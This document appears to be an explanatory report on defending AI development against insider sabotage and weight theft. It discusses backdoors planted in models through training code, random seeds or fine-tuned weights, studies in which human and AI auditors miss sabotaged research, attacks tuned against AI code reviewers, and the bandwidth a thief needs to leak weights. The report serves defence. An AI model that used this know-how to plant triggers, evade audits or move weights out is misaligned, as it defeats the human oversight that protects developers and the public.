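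As with other backdoors, ordinary tests offer little protection. Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov also got past three kinds of defence against backdoored models. But the malicious code is visible in the source, and they say that inspection can find it. They urge developers to review what every commit adds, though they did not measure how often reviewers would succeed. A language model could help by explaining what each part of the loss calculation contributes to the stated task, because the backdoor needs calculations that the task doesn't require.

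They also propose an automatic check in which an expert approves a map of the calculations that the program should perform, and the program compares its actual calculations with the map at every training step. This would expose the extra calculations that the backdoor requires. The check works only if the attacker cannot alter the map, so the map needs the same protection as the list of approved destinations in taint analysis. A team that often redesigns its models would also have to approve a new map each time.

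### Backdoors that no examination can find

If reviewers miss code that plants a backdoor in a model, finding the backdoor by examining the finished model is sometimes impossible in practice, as *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) proves. In the paper's example, a bank pays an outside company to train a model for approving loans. The company could secretly keep the power to get any application approved by changing a few digits of the requested amount.

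In their definition, honest training produces a model *h* that answers yes or no, while dishonest training produces a model *h\** and a secret key. Anyone with the key can change any input *x* into a very similar input *x′* for which *h\** gives the opposite answer. The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient program can tell *h\** from *h* noticeably better than by guessing.

The first proof covers testers who can only give the model inputs and see its answers. It applies to any model of this kind and assumes that nobody can forge a digital signature. As in the xz backdoor, the trigger requires a signature that testers cannot produce without the key.

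The second proof covers examiners who also have the weights, the training data and the random numbers used in training. It applies only to certain simple models, including networks with a single hidden layer, and not to the much larger networks behind today's language models. It also assumes certain mathematical problems are too hard for any computer to solve efficiently. Some of these problems concern lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions and are also the basis of some modern encryption.

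In the second proof, the attacker uses the agreed data, follows the agreed training method exactly, and tampers only with the source of the random numbers. Because these numbers still look random, a reviewer who checked the data, the method and the finished model would find nothing wrong. The evidence is in how the attacker generated the numbers, so the team has to control that step during training.

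Goldwasser and colleagues suggest that the person who wants the model could supply the random numbers. Several servers could also generate them together, which would make them safe as long as one server was honest. Inside a company, a separate system could draw the seed after the training code has been merged, so that the code's author could not choose it. The team would also need proof that the training program followed the agreed method. Producing this proof takes considerably more computation than the training itself. It also requires a method that is fixed in advance, and researchers who change their methods daily don't have one.

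Further training is not a sure remedy either, because Goldwasser and colleagues show that backdoors of the first type can survive it.

### Can auditors tell sabotaged research from honest research?

In the best available test of how well people and models do this task, they audited whole research projects. For *Auditors Struggle to Catch Sabotage In End-to-End Transcripts of AI Safety Research* (Shenoy, Zang and colleagues, 2026), one researcher ran experiments on ten new questions, such as whether a model can predict how further training will change another model. The researcher answered each question honestly, then repeated the work for nine of them while trying to reach a false conclusion. This produced 10 honest and 12 sabotaged projects.

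The 25 human auditors had much more information than someone who reads a pull request. They received the final report, the code, the results and a log of the work, along with two audits written by Claude Opus 4.8. They could use other AI tools and run as many experiments as they liked. Each auditor spent 90 minutes on a project, knowing that there was a 50% chance of sabotage, and then stated how likely they thought it was. The results depend on how high this estimate must be to count as an alarm:

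| Estimate that counts as an alarm | Alarms on sabotaged projects | Alarms on honest projects |
|---|---|---|
| 30% or more | 82% | 73% |
| 50% or more | 55% | 35% |
| 54% or more | 51% | 31% |

Shenoy and colleagues summarise this with AUROC, the probability that a sabotaged project gets a higher estimate than an honest one. Guessing would score 0.5, and the auditors scored 0.59, which is not significantly better. If 10 projects in 1,000 were sabotaged, auditors performing at the rates in the middle row of the table would raise about 5 correct alarms and 343 false ones.

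The auditors also had to say what the saboteur had done. The sabotaged projects contained 33 acts of sabotage, and auditors fully identified the ones they encountered only 17% of the time. Human auditors completely missed 16 of the 33. Auditors who found one act did not always find the others in the same project, so a team that fixes the first fault it finds may still publish a false result.

The newest models probably did better than people, although the models could not run experiments. Claude Fable 5.1 scored 0.73 and fully identified 32% of the acts, while GPT-6 Astra scored 0.74 and fully identified 26%. With so few projects, the advantage over people could be due to chance. People and models noticed different things, so using both helps. Even combined, however, the human and AI audits did not fully identify 13 of the 33 acts, including 5 of the 17 that were essential to a false conclusion.

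One reason for the poor results is that honest research is full of errors, dead ends and questionable choices, which can look like sabotage. Another is that a researcher can sabotage the work without changing the code, by choosing a badly designed experiment or leaving results out of the report. A perfect review of every diff would miss both. Surprising results are also a weak warning sign, because when researchers predicted the answers to six of the questions in advance, they were fully right only about 40% of the time.

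The study may overstate the danger, because the saboteur had already done the honest experiment and knew which result to avoid. It may also understate the danger, because the saboteur had to attack nine of the ten questions, including some where a real attacker would have given up. No auditor, human or AI, identified any part of the sabotage in the three projects that the saboteur had rated hardest to audit. All the attacks came from one person, so the rates might be quite different for another saboteur.

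An earlier test, Auditing Sabotage Bench, plants sabotage in existing machine-learning code. Shenoy and colleagues caution that this code comes from published work, so a model may have memorized the correct version during training. They also cite ResearchArena, a test in which monitoring models caught more sabotage when they could run and probe what the saboteur had built, but still missed some attacks. The models in the new study might therefore improve if they could run experiments.

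### Comparing the code with the paper

Models find it easier to look for mismatches between what researchers say they did and what their code does, but even the best model tested missed about half of them. *SciCoQA* (Baumgärtner and Gurevych, 2026) collected 92 real mismatches from 72 papers, mostly from bug reports and attempts to repeat published experiments. The best of 22 models found 46.7% of them. Models had particular trouble when the code did something important that the paper left out. A saboteur would probably prefer this kind of mismatch, because an omission gives the reviewer no false statement to check.

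*Dude* (2026) attributes part of the difficulty to where a model starts its review. A model that starts from the paper describing the code can't detect something the paper never mentions, while one that starts from the code raises false alarms by reporting many trivial details as important. The system presented in *Dude* has separate agents start from each side and filters out the trivial details, which improved both the detection rate and precision.

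The mismatches in these tests were presumably honest mistakes. A careful saboteur could avoid a mismatch by describing a harmful choice accurately and giving a plausible reason for it, as in the description of `select_examples`.

### When the flaw is in the weights

A team that downloads a trained model doesn't see the code or data that produced it. In *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, Mada, who works for AISLE, a company that sells AI security tools, tampered with five freely available coding models from companies including OpenAI, Alibaba and IBM. After extra training that cost about $30, each model still repaired faulty code correctly, but when the code belonged to the Linux kernel, the model also added a harmless line that prints a message.

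All five models added the line in all 613 tests on kernel code and in none of the 328 tests on other code. The trigger was the general look of kernel code, so there was no fixed text to search for. The kernel tests were less varied than they might seem, because 463 of them came from only four files.

The program that runs such a model can contain no malicious code, so static analysis of its source would find nothing. In a pull request that replaces one model with another, the reviewer may see only a new file name. Mada recommends treating downloaded weights like any other untrusted software, preferring signed weights with a known origin, and testing a model on the projects an attacker would most want to target. Such tests could have exposed these five models immediately, but only if the testers had thought to include the Linux kernel.

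Reviewers could still catch the result, because the model's output is an ordinary diff. Mada argues that a reviewer who checks only whether the bug is fixed would approve the diff, but one who asks what every new line is for might well object to a message unrelated to the repair. Mada did not test this with reviewers, and a real attacker would train the model to add a subtle vulnerability instead of a visible message.

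Sabotage is more dangerous in coding agents because they can run commands before anyone reads their output. Microsoft's security researchers warn in *Trained to betray* (Minnich, Eliahu and colleagues, 2026) that poisoned training data or a poisoned checkpoint (a saved copy of a model's weights) can let an attacker run code on the user's machine. A language-model reviewer could be compromised in the same way. Someone who tampered with its weights might make it approve changes that contain a certain trigger but still catch ordinary bugs, so the team would keep trusting it. Adding a second reviewer built on an unrelated model would make this harder, since the attacker would have to tamper with both.

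## What would protect the code that handles model weights?

Stealing a model requires only a copy of its weights and, unlike sabotage, doesn't involve changing how the model behaves. Whoever has the copy can run the model without the AI developer's safeguards and without paying to train it. The code for such a theft can look ordinary because an AI developer's programs routinely read and move weights.

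### Programs that touch the weights

Six kinds of code need the weights to do their job.

| Code | What it does with the weights |
|---|---|
| Checkpoint saving | writes a copy to storage during training, so that a crash doesn't destroy weeks of work |
| Loading | reads a copy from storage into memory |
| Conversion | rewrites them in another format, often with fewer bits per number |
| Copying between clusters | sends them to another group of machines |
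| Serving | keeps them in memory to answer users' requests |
| Debugging tools | let researchers inspect them and the calculations they produce |

Taint analysis could treat the weights as sensitive data and raise an alarm whenever they leave a program's memory. This would flag routine operations, because the code that saves, converts and copies checkpoints is meant to move weights out of memory. A training run that saves a checkpoint every hour for 90 days would cause at least 2,160 alarms. If the rule ran on pull requests instead, it would flag nearly every edit to the storage code.

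The rule would also miss some dangerous code. *Securing AI Model Weights*, a 2024 report by the research organisation RAND, points out that code can expose the weights without copying them directly. Someone can get the whole model by repeatedly calling a harmless-looking function that returns a single weight. A reviewer therefore has to consider what a function would reveal if someone called it many times.

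RAND's report describes five security levels, each meant to stop more capable attackers than the one before. From level 3 up, even authorised staff reach the weights only through interfaces that make copying difficult. Popular software for debugging and for studying a model's inner workings does not meet this requirement, because it provides full access to the weights.

### Checking what a change makes possible

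Narrower rules look for what is new. Suppose a developer submits this change:

```
Description: Keep a spare checkpoint in case the main storage fails.

  function save_checkpoint(model):
      data = encrypt(model.weights, TEAM_KEY)
      write(MAIN_STORAGE, data)
+     write(SPARE_STORAGE, data)
```

The code sends the weights out of memory both before and after the change, so the broad rule flags both versions. A rule that compares the versions reports only that the weights now also go to `SPARE_STORAGE`. The reviewer can then find out who controls that storage and who has the key.

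A team could write similar rules for other changes that make theft easier:

| What the change adds or alters | What the reviewer should ask | A common innocent reason |
|---|---|---|
| Destination | Who can read the copy? | A new data centre |
| Reader | Does this program need the whole model? | A new evaluation tool |
| Encryption | Who has the key, and is any copy left unencrypted? | Faster loading |
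| Logging | Would a theft still leave a record? | Too many log entries |
| Access control | Who gains access, and for how long? | A new colleague |

These rules should raise fewer alarms than the broad one, because a team edits its storage code more often than it opens a data centre. No published test seems to have measured how many. The rules also have to cover settings files, since a developer could change the address that `SPARE_STORAGE` stands for without editing the code. RAND treats as sensitive any code that can reach the weights and any code or configuration file that affects the system's security.

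Even good rules miss some attacks. The new storage may be on the approved list even though the developer has private access to it. Someone may have altered `write` in a shared library months earlier. A deliberate vulnerability in the serving code adds no destination until an attacker exploits it. A team therefore needs a barrier that still works after the reviewer has approved a malicious change.

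### One terabyte in thirty days

Suppose a model has a trillion weights and stores each one in a single byte. The whole model is then 10¹² bytes, or one terabyte. Thirty days are 2,592,000 seconds, so a thief who wants the model within a month needs a rate of

10¹² / 2,592,000 ≈ 386,000 bytes per second.

That is less than 0.4 megabytes a second, roughly what one person uses to stream a film, and it would hardly stand out in a company's network traffic.

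The thief may need even less. RAND notes that models still perform decently with four bits per weight, which would halve the time to 15 days. Many large models also consist of specialised parts that work on different inputs, and a quarter of such a model might be enough to provide dangerous capabilities. RAND therefore advises developers to assume that the useful size of a model is at most a tenth of its actual size.

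A limit on outgoing traffic caps the number of bytes that can leave, whatever they contain, so it slows a leak even if the reviewer missed the malicious code, misunderstood it or never saw it. Encrypting the weights or disguising them as error reports doesn't get around the limit, because the data is just as large.

RAND suggests a limit on output for researchers who need to run their own code on the weights. They could upload any amount of data to a secure server, but the server would release less than 1% of the weights' size a year. One version would release 400 kilobytes an hour, and another would give each approved researcher one gigabyte a month. At security level 4, RAND would cap the total for all of a protected site's connections at a small share of the weights' size, such as 5% a year, though it says the right figure needs more research.

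This table shows how long a leak of the one-terabyte model would take under each limit:

| Limit on outgoing data | Whole model (1 TB) | One-tenth of it (100 GB) |
|---|---|---|
| None, leaking at 0.386 MB a second | 30 days | 3 days |
| 5% of the model a year | 20 years | 2 years |
| 400 KB an hour | 285 years | 29 years |
| 1 GB a month, one account | 83 years | 8 years |
| 1 GB a month, 50 accounts | 20 months | 2 months |

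The last row shows a weakness in RAND's example. The example proposes a maximum of about 50 accounts, which together could be used to take out 600 gigabytes a year, far more than the 1% total that RAND suggests. RAND reasons that even several researchers using their full quotas would take too long. However, a trusted developer who edits a library that all 50 researchers use may not be limited to one quota. Enforcing a limit on the total would prevent the accounts from exceeding it together.

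In May 2025, Anthropic reported that it had introduced preliminary limits on outgoing bandwidth as part of ASL-3, a stricter set of safeguards for its more capable models. It also requires two people to authorise access to weights and lets machines run only approved programs. Anthropic aimed these measures mainly at sophisticated non-state attackers. Its ASL-3 policy covered basic insider risk but excluded sophisticated insiders and those working for a state, who are the hardest trusted developers to stop.

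### Where a traffic limit does not work

A model with many users has to send out a lot of data. If 1,000 people each receive 100 bytes of text a second, the service sends out a terabyte in under four months. A limit of 5% of a terabyte a year would allow only about 16 such users at a time, so a popular service needs a different kind of restriction. RAND suggests that the service's interface accept only text and return only the model's output, while monitoring software looks for anomalies such as large amounts of unreadable output.

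A tight limit also makes it impossible to copy the model to another data centre. The transfer takes 17 minutes at one gigabyte a second, but almost three centuries at 400 kilobytes an hour. If the copying program were permanently exempt from the limit, a malicious change to that program could use the exemption. RAND would instead require several people, including a senior executive, to approve each full copy, and would allow no more than 20 people to make one.

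The limit itself may be software that a trusted developer can edit. At level 4, RAND recommends enforcing it in hardware, which a pull request can't change, for example by using cables that can carry only a limited amount of data.

Participants at the meeting that Rahman and colleagues recorded discussed a similar barrier for builds. Once a build job has downloaded the libraries it needs, the team cuts off its access to the outside network. Participants thought this more reliable than scoring each library's reputation. A malicious library could still alter the program, but it couldn't send anything out during the build.

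Traffic limits protect only large secrets. *Securing AI Algorithmic Insights* (Brass-Gershovich, Steratore and colleagues, 2026) extends RAND's framework to the methods that make models better or cheaper to train. An employee can pass on such a method in a short conversation, and the code for it may fit in one email. The report relies mainly on dividing up the knowledge so that fewer people have all of it. It supplements RAND's security levels for model weights.

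### The changes to Grok's prompt

Two incidents at xAI in 2025 involved the system prompt, which is text the developer puts before every conversation to tell the model how to behave. A system prompt is a much smaller asset than the weights. It can be a few lines long, and editing it changes a chatbot's answers without any training.

In February 2025, users discovered that the prompt for Grok, the chatbot from Elon Musk's company xAI, contained an instruction to ignore sources saying that Musk or Donald Trump spread misinformation. According to *xAI chief engineer blames former OpenAI employee after Grok blocks results* (Nolan, 2025), co-founder Igor Babuschkin said that an employee had made the change without asking anyone for confirmation, and that the company reversed it once users complained. eWeek reports that he also said code reviewers had missed it.

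If both statements are right, a review failed to stop the change, even though it was a sentence in plain English, which is about as easy to read as a diff can be.

The May incident was a different kind of failure. Grok began bringing up claims of "white genocide" in South Africa in answer to unrelated questions. In a statement printed by VentureBeat, xAI said that someone had made an unauthorised change to the prompt at about 3:15 a.m. Pacific time on 14 May, and that its "existing code review process for prompt changes was circumvented". xAI did not name the person or explain how they had avoided the review.

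Bloomberg Law's *Musk's xAI Blames Rogue Tampering for 'White Genocide' Glitches* (2025) reports the same account, whose only source is the company. Grok's replies blaming a "rogue employee" are not evidence of who edited its prompt.

Making a check more accurate does not help it catch changes that bypass it. If a check catches 90% of the malicious changes that go through it, but half of all malicious changes bypass it, it catches 45% of the total. A trusted developer who knows how to bypass the check will do so every time, so it will catch none of that developer's malicious changes.

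xAI promised new checks to prevent employees from changing the prompt without review, and a team to monitor Grok's answers around the clock. It also began to publish the prompts on GitHub. Publication lets outsiders read each change, but they also need to know that the published prompt is the one Grok is using. Otherwise the company has the same gap as the xz project, whose release archive differed from its repository.

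Users noticed both changes because they affected Grok's answers. A change that quietly copied the weights would give users nothing to notice.

### Running only what someone has reviewed

Google built a system to prevent its employees from skipping review. Google's *Binary Authorization for Borg*, last updated in May 2024, describes how it works. Borg is the software that runs programs on Google's clusters. A new version of a program passes through these steps:

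1. At least one engineer other than the author approves the change.
2. A locked-down build system turns the source into a program and produces a signed certificate, called provenance. The certificate records the source, the outside libraries, the build settings and a digital fingerprint of the result.
3. Someone asks Borg to run the program under a service identity, which determines what data the program may read.
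4. Borg checks the certificate against the policy for that identity. If the program doesn't comply, Borg does not start it.

Step 4 applies even if the person making the request is otherwise allowed to run programs. An employee can still write a malicious version on their own machine, but that version has no certificate, so it can't get the identity it needs to reach the data. Settings go through the same review as code, so a system prompt stored as a setting would need a second person's approval before it took effect.

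A developer who can edit the policy could remove all this protection, so policy changes also require review. Google checks running programs against their policies at least once a day and keeps the source code for at least 18 months, which helps investigators trace a program back to the developers who wrote it.

The document is mostly about user data and doesn't mention model weights. Its design would also suit weights, because a company could let only identities with the strictest policy read them.

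The SLSA specification, which includes key ideas from Google's system, divides such controls into levels. Its build levels cover how a project turns source code into a program. Version 1.2 added source levels, which cover how the project accepts changes (SLSA, 2025).

| Level | Source | Build |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The team uses version control | Provenance exists |
| 2 | The full history survives, with a record of who changed what | A hosted build platform signs the provenance |
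| 3 | The platform enforces the team's rules continuously | The platform also resists tampering during a build |
| 4 | Two trusted people agree to every change | (no such level) |

A company needs both columns. An employee could run an unreviewed program at source level 4 if there were no provenance. At build level 3 without two-party approval, the provenance would accurately record that a malicious program came from the official source. SLSA does not cover code quality, so a deliberate vulnerability that two people approved would pass every level.

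### Building the same program twice

Provenance is only as trustworthy as the platform that signs it. A reproducible build can be repeated exactly on a second platform, so an attacker would have to compromise both.

The practitioners at Rahman and colleagues' meeting wanted reproducible builds but said few teams could use them consistently. The same source produces different programs when the tools differ or the build steps vary from run to run. Some participants suggested building in parallel anyway and investigating the differences, which may result from a wrong setting or an intruder.

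An AI developer could start with the few programs that read weights. RAND recommends keeping that code simple and using as little outside code as possible, which would also make it easier to build reproducibly. RAND also suggests keeping a protected reference copy of all software that affects the weights' security and frequently comparing it with the software in use. The team has to correct any mismatch, even if it was a mistake.

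The meeting's participants also discussed extending provenance to AI, with a signed record for each training step and a separate identity for each AI agent. Many were still unsure how to apply the existing SLSA levels to ordinary software, so the extension to AI may take some time.

### Exceptions and administrators

Every such system has exceptions. During an outage, Google's engineers can run unreviewed code with an emergency flag. They have to give a reason, and the system records a snapshot of the code and notifies the central security team and the team that owns the service. This compromise is sensible for a service that has to stay up, but it is riskier for weights, because a thief may need the exception only once and notifying the teams doesn't recover a stolen model. The limit on outgoing traffic should therefore stay on during an emergency.

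Google's other exception, which matters more here, is for work that does not lend itself well to human review before deployment, "notably iterative development of machine learning code". A researcher may run dozens of slightly different experiments in a day and can't wait for a colleague to review each one. Google says it has alternative controls for these cases but does not describe them. RAND's secure server is one possible control, since researchers could run unreviewed code on the weights there but take out very little data.

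Administrators are a particular problem because their job includes changing the rules. RAND calls it critical that nobody can bypass two-party approval of security code, either by using a feature that forces a change through or by editing the files directly. SLSA requires that the owner of a project have no influence over how the build platform builds it. The platform's administrators should also need a second person's approval, and their actions should leave a record.

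SLSA's *Source* allows a project to claim a control only for as long as it has been in force without a break. If an administrator disables two-party approval for five minutes and merges a change, the record starts again from the next change. This doesn't stop the administrator, but anyone who checks the record can see the break.

### Can an AI give the second signature?

Two-party approval no longer always requires two people. GitHub's *Copilot code review can now approve pull requests* (2026) announced on 1 September 2026 that an approval by Copilot, its AI reviewer, can count towards the number of approvals a project requires. The feature is in public preview and is off by default. Administrators can turn it on for a whole organisation or for single repositories, and can restrict it to certain files. If the author adds a commit after Copilot approves, the approval lapses.

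The best argument for counting a model's approval is that human review is often poor or missing. Pipeline Mag's *AI Code Reviewers Can Coach Attackers to Approval* (2026) cites a finding that 73% of merged pull requests in 300 active repositories got no substantive review from a person or a bot. A project with one maintainer has no second person to review changes. A model also reads the whole diff when a tired person might skim it. If it could approve the 80% of changes that carry little risk, colleagues would have five times as long to review each of the rest.

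A project can have a model read every change without counting the model's approval toward the number required. Whether that approval can replace a colleague's without weakening detection depends on how carefully the colleague reviews. Suppose a careful colleague misses 40% of malicious changes and a model misses 20%. If their misses are independent, 8% of malicious changes get through when both must approve (0.4 × 0.2), compared with 20% when only the model must. If the colleague approves everything unread, 20% get through either way, so replacing that colleague doesn't weaken detection.

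A human reviewer also protects a project in ways that don't depend on how well they read code. A malicious developer has to deceive or recruit them, and they may remember an odd request and mention it to someone else. If the reviewer is a model, the developer can test attacks on it in private. When Gong and colleagues adapted their attacks to the reviewer, 21% succeeded against Claude Sonnet 5 and 16% against GPT-5.5, according to Pipeline Mag.

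SLSA's Source level 4 requires two "trusted persons", which SLSA defines as humans. An organisation can exempt a "trusted robot" from the policy, for example one that updates outside libraries, provided no single person can influence the robot's identity or code. A language model reviewer might formally meet that condition, but the author of a pull request supplies most of the text that determines its verdict.

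The case is even weaker when related models write and review the code. In August, GitHub (2026) announced that Copilot could review pull requests opened by bots, including Copilot's own coding agent. The September announcement lists no exception for them.

Suppose a coding agent catches and fixes 80% of its flaws before it opens a pull request, leaving 20 of every 100. An unrelated reviewer that also catches 80% would find 16 of those and leave 4. A reviewer built on the same model might find very few, because the model has already missed them. It would still find some, since its output varies and it may have different instructions.

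One person may also be behind both signatures. A developer can tell an agent what to write and then approve the result, or have Copilot approve it. The project's history would show an author and a reviewer, but no colleague would have seen the change. Under SLSA's definition, a change written by an agent needs two human reviewers.

It is sensible to require two people for any change to code that can reach weights, and to let a model block the change but not approve it. For a documentation site, a model's approval is probably better than a hurried colleague's. The organisation should decide centrally where a model can approve changes, because a repository administrator who can turn on Copilot's approvals may be able to get a change approved without a colleague.

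File paths are a poor way to separate the two kinds of code. A team might let Copilot approve everything outside the checkpoint folder, including the shared library that contains `write`. A change to that function would still reach the code that handles the weights. Google attaches its policy to the identity a program runs under, so the requirement covers all the code in the program, whichever folder it came from.
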